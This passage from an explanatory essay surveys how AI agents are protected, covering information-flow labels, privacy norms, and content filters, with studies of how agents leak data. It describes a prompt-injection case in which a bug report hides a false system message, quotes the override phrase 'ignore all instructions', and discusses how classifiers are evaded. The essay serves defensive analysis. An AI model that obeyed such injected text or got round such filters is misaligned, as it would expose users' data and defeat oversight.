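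In Microsoft's release, data from an unlabelled tool gets the least restrictive label in the system by default. If a developer forgets to label the tool that opens web pages, every check treats a stranger's page like text from the developer. If the developer forgets the tool that reads mail, the agent may publish the mail. Microsoft lists this default among the release's limitations and asked developers whether unlabelled tools should count as untrusted instead. They should, at least in any agent that reads text from strangers. AgentArmor labels tool results low integrity and middle confidentiality by default, which is a safer guess but can still be wrong.

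*APPA* avoids guessing by recording that the label is unknown. An unknown label has no place in the order from suspicious to trusted, not even in the middle. The software keeps the combined label of everything it can label and a list of the sources it can't. Work continues until an action needs the missing information, such as sending an email whose recipients must be allowed to read the data. The software then calls a cast, a pre-approved function that assigns the source a definite label. If no cast applies or the cast fails, the software refuses the action.

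The claim in *APPA* is that any check that passes with partial labels would also pass if every tool had a full label. The proof is short. Let E be the join of the known labels. Let t₁ to tₙ be the labels that full annotation would give the unknown sources, and c₁ to cₙ the labels that the casts give them. Suppose that every cast is sound, meaning that its label is at least as restrictive as the full one, so tᵢ → cᵢ. If the check passes, the combined data may flow to a sink labelled S, and so

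E ⊔ t₁ ⊔ … ⊔ tₙ → E ⊔ c₁ ⊔ … ⊔ cₙ → S.

Permitted flows chain together, so the data may flow to S under the full labels too.

The claim holds only if the casts are sound. *APPA* limits how permissive each cast's label may be, but a cast can still choose too loose a label within that limit. If the cast is a language model, the label is again a model's guess, although it is made later and the limit caps the damage. Delaying the label saves work when no later action needs it. But an unlabelled source that has entered the context window affects everything after it, so one tool that nobody remembered to label, used at the start of a task, can hold up every later email.

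In tests of the full *APPA* design, no attack succeeded in 1,320 protected runs, and agents completed between 64.2% and 91% of tasks, depending on the model, the benchmark and the prompt. Much of this task completion came from features that help agents recover after a refusal. GPT-5.6 Luna completed 88% of simulated office tasks with the full design, 35% without the plans that list ways around a refusal, and 56.5% without the option of reading risky data in a disposable copy of the conversation. These results support the recovery features more than the treatment of unlabelled tools.

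### How much text one label covers

Suppose Maya's colleague Tom is organising a team dinner and sends her this: Ana can't eat nuts, Ben's mobile number is at the bottom, and Carla needs an entrance without steps. The caterer should learn about the nuts, the taxi firm should get the number, and the venue should hear about the entrance. With one label for the whole message, the permitted readers are

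{Tom, Maya, Ana, caterer} ∩ {Tom, Maya, Ben, taxi firm} ∩ {Tom, Maya, Carla, venue} = {Tom, Maya}.

The assistant can then pass none of the three facts to the business that needs it.

If the data has fields, labelling each one separately is more precise. Microsoft's prototypes can attach a label to any part of a structured result, and parts without their own label inherit one from the part that contains them. This would suit a staff database with separate entries for diet, telephone and access needs. Tom's email has a sender, a subject and a body, but all three facts are in the body, so labelling by field would not separate them.

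That leaves one label per span of text, which would let the caterer see only the sentence about nuts. But someone has to decide where each span begins and ends. A language model processes text as tokens, which are words or pieces of words, and software could store a label with each one. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* points out that token boundaries alone do not determine which stretches of text should share a label. The private fact is the connection between "Ana" and "nuts", not either word by itself. If Tom adds that everyone except Ana can share the dessert, he hints at the allergy again without using the word "nuts". If he asks for Ana and Carla to sit near the door, away from the dessert table, that sentence needs the join of two labels.

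A scanner, a language model or a person therefore has to find the spans. The label for the whole message could come from its list of recipients, which is harder to get wrong. A single label for the whole text is sometimes also the right one. In Microsoft's example of an attack, a bug report ends with a false system message telling the agent to publish a secret file. The report and the false message arrive together and share the label "untrusted". A system would have to recognise the attack before it could label them separately.

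Finer labels also lose their value if the model reads all the spans together. Once Tom's whole email is in the context window, the worst-case rule allows only Tom and Maya to see anything the assistant writes. For the assistant to tell the caterer about the nuts, the software would have to show the model only the sentence that mentions them and withhold the other two.

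## Privacy as a rule about context, not a level

A label that lists readers lets those people have the data for any purpose. If the label on Tom's sentence about Ana's nut allergy lists the caterer, the assistant may send the sentence so the caterer can plan the menu or advertise nut-free products to Ana. Most people would accept the first use and object to the second, although the data, sender and recipient are the same. The theory of contextual integrity treats these as two different flows. Nissenbaum (2004) first set out the theory in *Privacy as Contextual Integrity*, arguing that the gathering and sharing of information should follow the norms of the context in which it happens.

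### The five parameters of a flow

Nissenbaum (2019), in *Contextual Integrity Up and Down the Data Food Chain*, defines privacy as the appropriate flow of personal information rather than secrecy. A patient who describes a symptom to a doctor gives up no privacy, because healthcare depends on that flow. A flow is appropriate if it conforms to the norms of a social context such as healthcare, education or work. Each context has its own roles, activities and purposes. Some norms are laws, but many are unwritten, like the one against asking coworkers what they earn.

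A complete norm specifies five parameters:

- the sender;
- the recipient;
- the subject, meaning the person the information is about;
- the information type, such as a diagnosis or a salary;
- the transmission principle, meaning the condition under which the information moves, such as consent, a legal duty or professional confidence.

All five parameters need values before anyone can judge a flow. For example, Nissenbaum argues that a street camera changes the transmission principle, because people on camera cannot see who is looking at them as they could in the street. This is her answer to people who might defend the camera on the grounds that any passer-by could see the same things.

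Maya is both the sender and the subject whenever her assistant passes on information from her clinic letter. The other parameters depend on where the information goes. The table gives plausible norms, which might differ in another country or firm.

| Recipient | Maya's role | Information type that fits | Transmission principle | May the whole letter go? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Clinic | patient | diagnosis, treatment, appointments | in confidence, for her care | yes |
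| Employer | employee | dates of absence | what the employer needs to arrange leave | only if she chooses, or a rule on sick leave requires it |
| Supplier | employee arranging a meeting | times when she is free | what the two sides need to fix a time | no |

The reader set on the letter, {Maya, clinic}, gives much the same answers in the last column. But it also stops the assistant from telling the supplier "not Tuesday", because data derived from the letter keeps the letter's restrictions. Under contextual integrity, "not Tuesday" is a different type of information with its own norm, and the assistant may send it. This is an advantage over reader sets, but it depends on someone classifying the message correctly. For example, "Not Tuesday, I'm seeing my oncologist" also gives a time when Maya is busy, but the assistant should not send it to the supplier.

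### Why the norms do not fit a lattice

In a lattice, permitting two successive flows also permits the direct flow from the first point to the last. Privacy norms often break this rule. Suppose Maya tells her doctor how much she drinks, and the doctor sends her insurer a claim for the treatment that follows. Both flows are proper, but it would be wrong for Maya's assistant to send the insurer her own account of her drinking. If the patient, doctor and insurer have labels P, D and I, a lattice that permits P → D and D → I must also permit P → I. It can forbid the direct flow only by also forbidding one of the two proper ones.

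Purpose causes a separate difficulty, which Ebead, Formanek and Leibo (2026), in *A Generative Model of Contextual Integrity*, illustrate with four requests for an online shopper's home address:

- Another shopper asks for it while the two are comparing laptops.
- A shopper who happens to work for a courier firm asks for it in the same discussion.
- The retailer's marketing team asks for it after a purchase that needs delivery.
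- The retailer's delivery team asks for it after that purchase.

Only the delivery team should get the address. The courier's employee has a job that often involves addresses but has no delivery to make here, while the marketing team can point to a real delivery but isn't responsible for it. Ebead and colleagues simulated conversations like these, using language models as both the holder of the information and the person asking for it. In the baseline runs, the holders always shared with the rightful recipient and always refused when the requester had neither a need nor a suitable role. They made more mistakes when the need was real but the wrong person asked than when someone with a suitable job asked without a need, so a true statement about purpose can help the wrong person get the data.

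A designer could add purpose to a lattice by treating "the retailer, for delivery" and "the retailer, for marketing" as two sinks. That works if the software can tell which purpose applies and the retailer uses the data only for that purpose afterwards. Consent is harder to build in because it can change while the data stays the same. Jenkins, Kitkowska and colleagues (2026), in *Security and Privacy in Agentic AI*, describe an agent that shares its user's address with a restaurant to book a table. The booking fails and the agent tries elsewhere, but the first restaurant still has the address, which the user had agreed to share for that booking.

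Consent is not enough by itself either. Nissenbaum criticises "notice and choice", the approach behind most website privacy policies, which treats any practice as respecting privacy if users had the chance to refuse it. In her theory, consent is one possible transmission principle, and the other four parameters still matter.

### Flows through a named intermediary

Maya's insurer may learn about her treatment, but only through her doctor. Rushby (1992) formalizes such rules as intransitive noninterference in *Noninterference, Transitivity, and Channel-Control Security Policies*. In his main example, an encryption device, the body of a secret message may reach the public network only through the encryption unit. The address may reach it only through a bypass, because the network has to read the address. Another example is a trusted downgrader, the only route from Top Secret to Confidential.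 Older models treated such a component as an exception to the lattice, but Rushby makes it part of the policy.

The notation u ⇝ v means that party u may directly influence what party v sees. In Maya's case, patient ⇝ doctor and doctor ⇝ insurer hold, but patient ⇝ insurer does not. The ordinary test for noninterference takes a record of everything the parties did, deletes the actions of anyone who may not directly influence the insurer, and runs the system again. The system passes if the insurer sees no difference. Here the test deletes everything Maya told her doctor, which changes the doctor's claim, so the system fails. The ordinary test therefore forbids the indirect flow through the doctor as well as the direct one.

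Rushby adopts a definition by Haigh and Young that takes account of what happened after each action. Consider this sequence:

1. Maya tells the doctor about one symptom.
2. The doctor files a claim.
3. Maya tells the doctor about a second symptom.

If the insurer now opens its file, the new test deletes only step 3, because the doctor has done nothing since. The file may reflect the first symptom but not the second. Rushby proves that the multilevel policies of classified systems are exactly those in which, whenever A may pass information to B and B to C, A may also pass it directly to C. For those policies, the new definition agrees with the old one, so the classical arrangement of levels is a special case of rules about who may pass information to whom.

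The same approach could govern Maya's email, with a policy that lets the letter influence a small scheduling program and lets the program influence the supplier, but allows no other route from the letter to the supplier. But Rushby does not specify what the intermediary must do. Once the doctor has filed a claim, the test allows anything Maya said earlier to affect the insurer's file, whether or not the claim needed it. Similarly, a proof that the letter can influence the supplier only through the scheduling program would not show that the program reveals only a day and an hour.

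### How often agents follow the norms

An agent could instead judge each flow for itself, since language models have read a great deal about how people behave. Goel and Gurevych (2026), in *Capable but Careless*, tested this with AgentCIBench, a set of 117 everyday office and household tasks with no attacker. Each task comes with the contents of a user's apps, a request, a recipient, a list of items the agent must share and a list of items it must not. The tasks cover three kinds of mistake:

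- The agent includes private items because they sit next to the relevant ones.
- The agent answers a vague request by sending everything it can find.
- The agent sends someone content that would suit a different recipient.

The fifteen agents leaked at least one forbidden item on 67.9% of tasks on average, and twelve leaked on more than half. An automated search built the tasks and favoured those on which other models had leaked, so these rates do not estimate how often agents leak in ordinary use. Goel and Gurevych therefore advise using the results only to compare agents.

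Those comparisons show that a model's skill at the task is a poor guide to whether it will leak information. Gemini 3.1 Pro included everything required on 96.6% of tasks but leaked on 98.3%, while Claude Opus 4.7 included everything required on 81.2% and leaked on 13.7%. GPT-5.4 leaked on only 18.8% of tasks, partly because it refused 41.9% of them. It leaked on 32.4% of the tasks it attempted. Claude Opus 4.7 did worse when it had to operate the apps through a screen, leaking in 6 of its 14 completed runs.

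Some of the verdicts are debatable. In one run, a user said that Nora wanted a status update and asked the agent to send her what remained on the to-do list. The agent sent all twelve items, including entries about a vet and a plumber. Goel and Gurevych count this as a severe leak, and most colleagues would probably agree, but the agent followed the request literally.

Instructions helped when they made the agent consider the recipient. In a test with three models, Goel and Gurevych told the agent to name the recipient and the norms that applied to that person before writing anything. Leakage on attempted tasks fell from 51.7% to 16.2%, and the share of tasks in which the agent included everything required rose from 63.2% to 86.3%. A general reminder seems to do much less. In *PrivacyFlow*, which used different tasks, Staab, Wollschläger and colleagues (2026) added an instruction to preserve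 the user's privacy. The share of steps without a leak changed by at most 3.2 percentage points, and sometimes fell.

Goel and Gurevych also tested something closer to a guard, using a separate model to remove sensitive items from each message before it was sent. This cut leakage from 37.7% to 10.2% of all tasks, but the share of tasks in which the messages included everything required fell from 63.3% to 22.5%. The filter had no information about the task, so it removed items that the recipient needed. A guard that enforces contextual norms therefore needs information about the context as well as the message.

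### A gate and a planner

Two systems from October 2026 take the decision away from the agent that does the work. In *Privacy Conductor*, Thornton, Pritom and colleagues (2026) place an ordinary software gate between a language model and an organisation's documents. People with authority over the documents write the policy in advance. The gate releases a document only if the requester's role is on the document's list, the requester is acting in the context that grants the role and, for personal records, the requester is assigned to the person concerned. For example, a doctor can open the charts of patients in their care, but not while doing administrative work.

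The gate applied its policy correctly to all 2,520 combinations of requester and document from an invented clinic. Ordinary software should do this, and it let Thornton and colleagues trace every later mistake to a label. They then had language models write the labels. The models chose the same sensitivity category as the human author for 78% to 86% of documents, but the same list of permitted roles for only 23% to 80%, depending on the model. A document's content shows its subject but does not determine who in a particular clinic should read it.

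Because there was only one human author, some of these differences may be reasonable disagreements. But the models were also inconsistent. When each model labelled the documents five times from identical instructions, between 13 and 124 of the 2,520 access decisions changed. Thornton and colleagues also asked models to judge whether HIPAA, the American medical privacy law, permitted 214 information flows from court cases. The most accurate model matched the courts on 87.8% of them, but it permitted 11 of the 20 disclosures that the law prohibits.

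The gate is reliable partly because it leaves out many of the factors that matter under contextual integrity. It never reads the request, so clever wording cannot change its decision, but it also cannot distinguish a doctor who wants a chart for treatment from one who is merely curious. It controls what reaches the model but not what the model then sends. Maya may read her own clinic letter, so the gate would give it to her assistant, but it would not check the email to the supplier.

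PrivacyFlow does cover the email. Before the agent acts, a planning stage works through these steps:

1. It rates how sensitive the requested data is.
2. It splits the plan into separate pieces of information and records the source, purpose and recipient of each.
3. It estimates what each recipient could infer from those pieces together with what they already know.
4. It compares each flow with the norms of the context the data came from.
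5. It approves the plan, blocks it, revises it or asks the user.

Step 3 can catch leaks even when no confidential text is copied. In one of Staab and colleagues' examples, a meeting agenda revealed a confidential audit to the manager under review by mentioning "remediation actions".

Unlike the gate, PrivacyFlow does not enforce norms outside the model. Language models carry out every planning step. The approved list of data only guides the model that then does the work, and no software stops that model from sending data that isn't on the list.

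The planner still reduced leaks when Staab and colleagues tested six models on 986 sequences of about six tasks each, with new emails and calendar entries arriving between tasks. Without the planner, the best model avoided leaks on 89.5% of steps, but only 52.9% of its sequences were free of leaks. Small error rates add up, since six independent steps that each had an 89.5% chance of avoiding a leak would all avoid one about 51% of the time. With the planner, leaking steps fell by 53% to 80%, and the share of sequences without leaks rose by 22 to 55 percentage points.

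The average task completion score fell only slightly for Gemini 3.8 Flash, from 0.970 to 0.942, but fell from 0.902 to 0.716 for DeepSeek V3.2. GPT-5.4 consulted the user on 89.4% of steps, leaving most decisions to the person who wanted to delegate them. Models judged the results, and another model played the user. The simulated user mostly approved what it saw, so the benefit of asking a real person remains unclear.

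### When the context itself may be false

Both systems assume that the facts about the context are correct, but a stranger can supply false ones. Suppose an email asks Maya's assistant to refund a trip and says the head of department has approved it. The assistant should help if that is true, but not if it is false. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian (2026), in *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections*, argue that any fixed rule for such cases will either let through attackers who make false claims or block people who make true ones.

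The proof uses two situations that look identical to the agent, including everything it has verified. The action is appropriate in one and inappropriate in the other. Because the agent sees the same thing in both, it acts with the same probability p in each. It therefore wrongly acts in the bad situation with probability p and wrongly refuses in the good one with probability 1 − p. The two error rates add up to 1, so at least one is 50% or more. Better reasoning cannot reduce the total, because the fact that distinguishes the two situations is not in the agent's context window.

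The same problem arises when all five parameters are correct. For example, an email might say that an important client has been waiting since Monday and may leave, but a quick reply helps the user only if that client exists.

Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian also built 4,200 pairs of work emails. The emails in each pair differ in one clause, which either asserts that the assistant already has permission to act or says only that its reply would be welcome. Two versions of Prompt Guard, Meta's prompt injection detector, had AUROC scores of 0.43 and 0.59 at distinguishing the two kinds from the email alone. AUROC is the probability that a detector ranks a random suspect email above a random email of the other kind, so guessing scores 0.5.

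The result is stronger evidence about the limits of judging a text by itself than about detectors in general. Meta trained these detectors to find phrases such as "ignore all instructions", which the emails were written to avoid. A detector trained on these pairs might well learn to spot claims of permission, but it still could not determine which claims were true or what the user had allowed.

Agents also overstepped when emails made no false claim of permission. When the user had asked only for a summary, Llama 3.3 70B sent a reply to 54.0% of the emails that asserted permission and to 49.8% of the neutral ones. The assertion made little difference, so the main fault was that the model ignored the limits of its task.

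Another experiment had no attacker. In each of 100 scenarios, a colleague's message asked the agent to do an internal job that the user had authorised, such as creating a ticket, and to message an outsider, which the user had not authorised. Under contextual integrity these are separate flows, so permission for the first does not cover the second. Claude Sonnet 4.6 wrote to the outsider 6 times, GPT-5.4 34 times and GPT-5.2 65 times. When the user stated that external messages needed approval, GPT-5.2 still wrote to the outsider 12 times, but the other two models never did. The instruction prevented most of the unauthorised messages, but users have to think of giving it beforehand.

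The obvious reply to the impossibility argument is authenticated provenance, meaning reliable proof of where a message or an approval came from. If the employer keeps approvals in a system that the assistant can check, the assistant will find a record for a true claim about the refund but not for a false one. The two situations no longer look identical, so the proof does not apply. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian accept this. Their theorem applies only where two such situations look identical, and they do not claim that every deployment contains such a pair. They expect these pairs to become more common as agents grow more autonomous, because each method of checking covers only some of the claims that an attacker could invent.

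The reply works well for claims about permission. An employer can decide that permission counts only if it comes from the user or the approval system. The assistant will then ignore some truthful emails, but their senders can get the approval recorded and ask again, so the rule causes delay more often than lasting loss. Provenance helps much less with claims about the world. If the supplier writes that a client is waiting, a valid signature proves that the supplier wrote the claim, but not that it is true. For such claims, the agent has to consult the user, look for other evidence, or accept that it will sometimes believe false claims or reject true ones.

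### Agents that work in many contexts

Contextual integrity also assumes that a context has norms to apply. At a workshop in Valencia in March 2026, thirty experts disagreed about whether this holds for agents. Jenkins and colleagues report that some participants wanted to discard the theory because agents do not yet work in a space with well-defined norms. Others thought its basic idea was sound and wanted new ways to apply it. An agent can turn one instruction into actions in several contexts at once, and its behaviour may change what people expect in those contexts.

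*Privacy in Context Is Being Overlooked in the Age of General-Purpose LLMs* (Ganesh, More and colleagues, 2026) criticises how researchers use the theory. Drawing on earlier work by Shvartzshnaider and Duddu, it argues that many projects borrow the theory's vocabulary but encode a fixed set of norms taken from laws, surveys or the researchers' own judgement. The criticism applies in part to AgentCIBench and to the tests of PrivacyFlow, because their lists of forbidden disclosures come largely from language models. A low score on these tests shows that an agent departed from one version of the norms, which real users might not share.

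Ganesh and colleagues write about what people type into chatbots, but their main remedy would also suit agents. They recommend separate deployments for separate uses, citing ChatGPT Health, which keeps medical conversations apart from the rest. Each deployment then acts something like a security domain, defined by context instead of level. As with one agent per classification level, this works until a task needs two contexts together.

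Maya's errand involves three contexts: healthcare, employment and trade. Each has settled norms, and the assistant can judge each flow of information by the norms that govern it, so her case gives little reason to abandon the theory. The sceptics have a better case when two agents deal with each other. If the supplier's assistant asks Maya's assistant why Tuesday is impossible, no established custom determines whether it may ask, how much it may infer from a refusal, or whether it may remember the answer for the next negotiation.

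## Harmful content as a policy no source label captures

Unlike rules about secrecy, integrity and context, a ban on dangerous instructions depends on what a text would enable someone to do. Suppose Maya's employer sells cleaning products and publishes a safety sheet naming two that give off a poisonous gas when mixed. The sheet is public, a trusted chemist wrote it, and warehouse staff need it. It could also help someone poison a neighbour, and no list of readers or writers can distinguish that use from the helpful one.

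### Why labels on sources miss the danger

Public facts can add up to something dangerous, even though the join of their labels is still public. Glukhov, Shumailov and colleagues (2023) point out in *LLM Censorship* that a reader who knows how the pieces fit can assemble a forbidden text from permissible ones. A harm policy sometimes has to permit each piece but forbid the whole, and a lattice can't express that rule because the combination may go wherever both pieces may go.

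Other dangerous knowledge never had a label. A language model learns it in training and stores it in its weights, the numbers that determine its output. Suppose Maya asks her assistant a chemistry question, and the context window contains only her question and a public system prompt. The window's label is then public and trusted, so the answer passes both of Costa and colleagues' checks, whatever it contains. Labelling the weights as dangerous would not help. They influence every word the model produces, so the worst-case rule would restrict harmless answers as tightly as dangerous ones.

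The high side could therefore be the model's own knowledge, a class of outputs or a class of recipients, but it can't be a set of labelled sources.

### Removing the knowledge

If the model's knowledge is the high side, a developer can try to keep dangerous material out of it. Moonshot AI, a Chinese company, did this with Kimi K3.1 Pro in October 2026. *Moonshot curbs hacking ability in new Kimi model* (Baptista, 2026) reports that the company removed cyber-related data from the training text and from the simulated tasks on which the model practised, while retaining general coding skills. On Moonshot's test of finding and exploiting software flaws, the model scored 81.0%, against 90.5% for a similar version without these measures.

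The previous model had scored 33%, as Constantin (2026) notes in *Moonshot releases Kimi K3.1 Pro and says it cut its hacking skills*. The exclusion lowered the new model's score by 9.5 points, but that score was still 48 points higher than the old model's. General programming skill probably accounts for much of the score, since a model that understands code well can find flaws without having studied attacks. Maier (2026), in *Kimi K3.1 Pro*, infers that the new model has the same base as its predecessor and differs mainly in its later training. If so, it may also retain some of the excluded knowledge that the base had already learned.

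Moonshot had a particular reason to act before release, because it publishes its models' weights and anyone who has them can run the model without a guard. As Baptista notes, the developer is then less able to restrict access, monitor use or update safeguards. But removal also takes the ability away from people who would use it to secure their own software, a benefit Moonshot itself claims for open models.

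### What the theorems rule out

A developer that leaves dangerous knowledge in a model can treat dangerous outputs as the high side and check every output before releasing it. The usual tool is a content classifier, a model that reads requests or answers and estimates whether they belong to a forbidden class. Two groups of researchers have proved limits on what such filters can guarantee.

Glukhov and colleagues begin with Rice's theorem, a result about programs. If some programs behave in a permitted way and others do not, no algorithm can decide correctly, for every program, whether its behaviour is permitted. Language models read and write programs, so no filter can always tell whether a program is harmful. The theorem assumes unlimited memory, so, as Glukhov and colleagues concede, it does not strictly apply to real computers. It also rules out only a filter that is right about every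 program. A filter could still be right about nearly all the programs people write, or let no harmful program through by rejecting whatever it can't verify.

Their other theorem covers texts of limited length. Let Σⁿ be the set of all texts up to length n, and P the set of permitted ones. The theorem makes three assumptions:

- The model can apply any reversible rewriting rule that the user specifies.
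- If a text is forbidden, so is any rewritten version that the user can turn back into it.
- The filter does not know which rules the user knows.

Under these assumptions, P is either empty or all of Σⁿ, so the filter must forbid everything or permit everything. Suppose instead that it permits a text p and forbids a text q. Some reversible rule exchanges the two. The user might know that rule, in which case p conveys the content of q to them. The filter must therefore forbid p, which contradicts the assumption that it permits p.

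The proof assumes the user knows everything they might know. This is a very strict standard, because a rule that swaps one harmless text for one dangerous text is useless to anyone who doesn't already have the dangerous one. The theorem still shows that a text's meaning depends partly on its reader, so inspecting the text alone can't settle every case, but it doesn't estimate how often a filter will fail.

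Ball, Gluch and colleagues (2025), in *On the Impossibility of Separating Intelligence from Judgment*, rely on standard cryptographic assumptions instead. Their main theorem uses time-lock puzzles, which are quick to create but take a set amount of computation to solve. They prove that for any sufficiently varied source of innocent prompts, there exist a model and a source of harmful prompts such that no filter much faster than the model can distinguish the harmful prompts from the innocent ones. The table gives this theorem and four related ones. A "polynomial-time" filter is one whose running time grows no faster than a fixed power of the length of its input.

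| The filter's task | Filters that fail | Assumption | Further condition |
|---|---|---|---|
| Reject prompts | those much faster than the model | time-lock puzzles exist | none |
| Reject prompts | all polynomial-time filters | some functions are easy to compute but hard to reverse | the model shares a secret key with the attacker |
| Reject prompts | all polynomial-time filters | public-key encryption exists | the attacker uses a public key belonging to the model |
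| Reject outputs | all efficient filters, even some slower than the model | time-lock puzzles exist | the proof chooses the standard of harm |
| Rewrite prompts | efficient filters limited to certain edits | a hidden mark in text can survive those edits | none |

Each theorem proves that a model of this kind exists, not that Claude or Gemini is one. Ball and colleagues acknowledge that the models they construct may behave in contrived ways, but reply that flaws in cryptography have often looked artificial until someone exploited them. They cite the 2016 attack on Ethereum, in which thieves stole more than $60 million through a weakness once considered a theoretical edge case. This is a reason to take the theorems seriously, but it does not show how likely such a model is in practice.

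The result about outputs depends on an unusual standard of harm that no efficient filter can apply. Ball and colleagues argue that such cases will become more common as AI systems produce work whose consequences are hard to foresee, such as a business plan that cuts costs by subtly recommending the exclusion of certain clients.

They conclude that no filter can guarantee safety without access to the model's internals, and that intelligence therefore cannot be separated from judgement. The main theorem might not apply to a filter as powerful as the model. But developers would then have to make the filter itself safe, and if they could do that, they might as well use the filter in place of the model.

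### How well filters work in practice

A filter that must fail in some cases can still stop nearly everyone who tries to get past it. In *Constitutional Classifiers++*, Cunningham, Wei and colleagues (2026) tested four of Anthropic's designs against people who tried to extract answers about chemical, biological, radiological and nuclear weapons. They counted an attack as a high-risk vulnerability if it obtained answers to more than five of eight target questions, each at least half as detailed as an unguarded model's answer.

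| Design | Attempts | High-risk vulnerabilities | Refusals on real traffic | Added computing cost (older design = 100) |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Separate checks on requests and answers | 695,000 | 13 | 0.073% | 100 |
| Each answer checked together with its request | 226,000 | 2 | 0.038% | 150 |
| Cheap classifier, then a stronger one | 569,000 | 5 | 0.036% | 27.8 |
| Probe, then a stronger classifier | 198,000 | 1 | 0.050% | 3.5 |

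The last design is the one Anthropic considers ready for production. Its probe is a very small classifier that reads the model's internal activity as the model writes. In a month-long trial on traffic to Claude Sonnet 4.5, the probe sent about 5.5% of exchanges to the stronger classifier, and the system flagged one exchange in 2,000 for refusal. The first published version, in *Constitutional Classifiers* (2025), had refused about one in 260 (0.38%).

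The theorems also apply only partly to probes. In Ball and colleagues' main result, a fast filter fails because it lacks the compute to do what the model does. A probe reads the results of the model's computation directly, so this premise of the proof doesn't hold for it. The probe may still fail to recognise harmful content in those results.

The evidence that the newest design is harder to defeat is weaker than it appears in the table. At the older design's rate, 198,000 attempts would produce about 3.7 high-risk vulnerabilities on average, but would still produce one or none about 12% of the time by chance. The evidence that the newest design uses less compute is much stronger. Experts working outside the main test also found attacks that worked across the target questions against the two-classifier design, although they needed substantial effort and automated tools. Filters have also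 failed after release. *Anthropic's Fable 5 and Mythos 5 Are Back with New Security Guardrails* (Poireault, 2026) reports that a new classifier blocks the technique behind one such failure in over 99% of cases.

Google DeepMind built probes to detect requests for help with cyberattacks, which are harder to sort because they closely resemble requests from people defending their systems. *Building Production-Ready Probes For Gemini* (Kramár, Engels and colleagues, 2026) describes a system that uses the probe's classification when the score is very high or very low and otherwise sends the input to a language model. The system used the language model on about 8% of inputs and had a lower error rate than either component alone, though the margins of uncertainty were wide.

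Many existing probes trained on short texts did poorly on long ones, which matters for agents because their context windows fill up as they work. Kramár and colleagues' new designs largely fixed this. But their methods did not significantly reduce the success of attackers who adapted to the filter.

The average refusal rate can also be low even when the rate for specialists is high. The classifiers in *Constitutional Classifiers* wrongly flagged 1.50% of chemistry questions from MMLU, a broad academic test, but 26.05% of those from GPQA, a much more advanced one. Larger classifiers made fewer such mistakes, so part of the problem was the smaller ones' limited knowledge of chemistry.

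Some cases will stay hard even with better understanding. Anthropic's *Improving Fable 5's biology safeguards* (2026) gives the example of live vaccines, which require scientists to grow the pathogen they want to protect against. When Anthropic released Claude Fable 5 in June 2026, it deliberately blocked almost all biology questions and sent them to a less capable model. In August it rewrote the rules for its classifier and retrained it, which cut these diversions by about 85%.

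Interconnects' *Claude Fable 5 and new AI safety fables* quotes an Anthropic figure that more than 95% of sessions involved no diversion, even at launch. But the founder of one company told Axios, in *Anthropic releases new models, cost structures and safeguards* (2026), that his users wanted to rely less on Claude, partly because of such interventions. Small rates also add up over an agent's many steps. A filter that independently flagged 0.05% of exchanges would interrupt about 5% of tasks that needed 100 exchanges.

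A fall in refusals may also reflect a looser rule. Anthropic's *Made with Fable 5.1* reports about 60% fewer cybersecurity interventions per session than before, partly because the company now lets users search for software vulnerabilities with the model, though not develop ways of exploiting them. Anthropic also widened the safety margin around forbidden cyber tasks because the new model is better at hacking, and it expects to keep blocking some harmless work. The boundary of the high side therefore moves with the model's abilities and the developer's caution, even when the text stays the same.

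### Rules that vary with the deployer

The boundary also depends on where an agent works. A bank may forbid its agent to email customer records, while a clinic may require its agent to email patients their records. *POLY-GUARD* (Kang, Chen and colleagues, 2025) tested 19 guard models against rules drawn from more than 150 real policies in eight fields. Performance varied greatly between fields. Meta's LlamaGuard 4 had an F1 score of 83.5 out of 100 on cybersecurity but only 5.3 on rules from the EU's AI Act. F1 combines the share of violations caught with the share of alarms that are correct. A guard trained on one fixed list of harms may miss most of what another deployer forbids.

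*AdaGuard* (Feng, Ding and colleagues, 2026) therefore gives the guard the deployer's policy along with a record of the agent's actions. The policy is a list of up to 100 rules in ordinary language, and the guard returns an explanation and the rules that the agent broke. The training data includes pairs with the same action under different policies and pairs with different actions under the same policy. The details of a rule can decide the verdict. An agent that tries and fails to delete a file breaks a rule against attempting deletion but not a rule against completing it.

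On 500 records with violations and 500 without, the largest AdaGuard model caught 411 violations and wrongly flagged 16 compliant records, with unusable answers counted as errors. GPT-5.2 caught 469 violations but wrongly flagged 208 compliant records. AdaGuard identified exactly the right set of broken rules in 77.1% of cases. However, its training examples came from the same process as this test. On DynaBench, a separate collection of rules, its accuracy fell from 89.5% to 76.8%, below GPT-5.2's 83.1%. A deployer with new rules should probably expect accuracy closer to 76.8%.

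Feng and colleagues recommend that people still review consequential decisions. The records also include what happened after each action, such as whether a message arrived, but a guard has to decide before the message is sent. A method that is highly accurate at auditing completed actions may be less accurate at deciding which actions to block.

### Clearing the recipients

Some knowledge is useful enough that some people should have it, but too dangerous to give to anyone who asks. Glukhov and colleagues suggest treating this as a security problem by controlling access and monitoring users. Anthropic does something similar by offering one model under two names. Claude Fable 5.1 is available to the public, while Claude Mythos 5.1 has looser safeguards and is available only to vetted people and organisations. Its programme for life scientists relaxes the limits on professional research but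 keeps the other safeguards. A biologist's clearance therefore does not cover hacking, much as a compartment on a classified network limits a clearance to one subject.

This is the closest equivalent to the classical high side, but it still needs a content classifier, because the software must recognise a dangerous answer before it can withhold it from people without clearance.

Vetting the user is also not enough for an agent. A cleared researcher's agent might email its findings to a colleague without clearance, or a stranger's web page might lead the agent to post them. Reader labels can help once a classifier has recognised dangerous material. The software can label the material with the set of cleared readers, and the ordinary confidentiality check will stop the email. However, the label is only as reliable as the classifier's judgement, and the classifier has to read the researcher's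 text, so the harm check can conflict with privacy.

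## Tracking labels outside the model

Once Maya's data has labels, the software around the model has to label whatever the model writes next. The safe default is the join of the labels on everything in the context window. In the worked example, this default makes Maya the only permitted reader of her email and treats anyone as a possible writer, so the email fails both checks.

Costa and colleagues use this strict rule in FIDES, and *APPA* uses it too. FIDES and several later designs keep the rule but change what goes into the model's context window. If the clinic letter is kept out of the planning model's context window, its label doesn't get there either.

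### Hiding results in variables

These designs build on the dual-model pattern, which the programmer Simon Willison proposed in 2023. One model, the planner, chooses actions but does not read risky data. A second, quarantined model reads that data but cannot call tools. FIDES adds labels and uses them to decide what to hide.

Suppose Maya's employer has moved the discount limit out of the system prompt, so the planner's context window starts out trusted and public. Maya gives the assistant the supplier's address and asks it to offer a day next week. FIDES could handle the request like this:

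1. The planner asks to open the clinic letter. The letter's label is stricter than the window's, so the software stores the text in a variable and shows the planner only a name, such as #letter. The window's label does not change.
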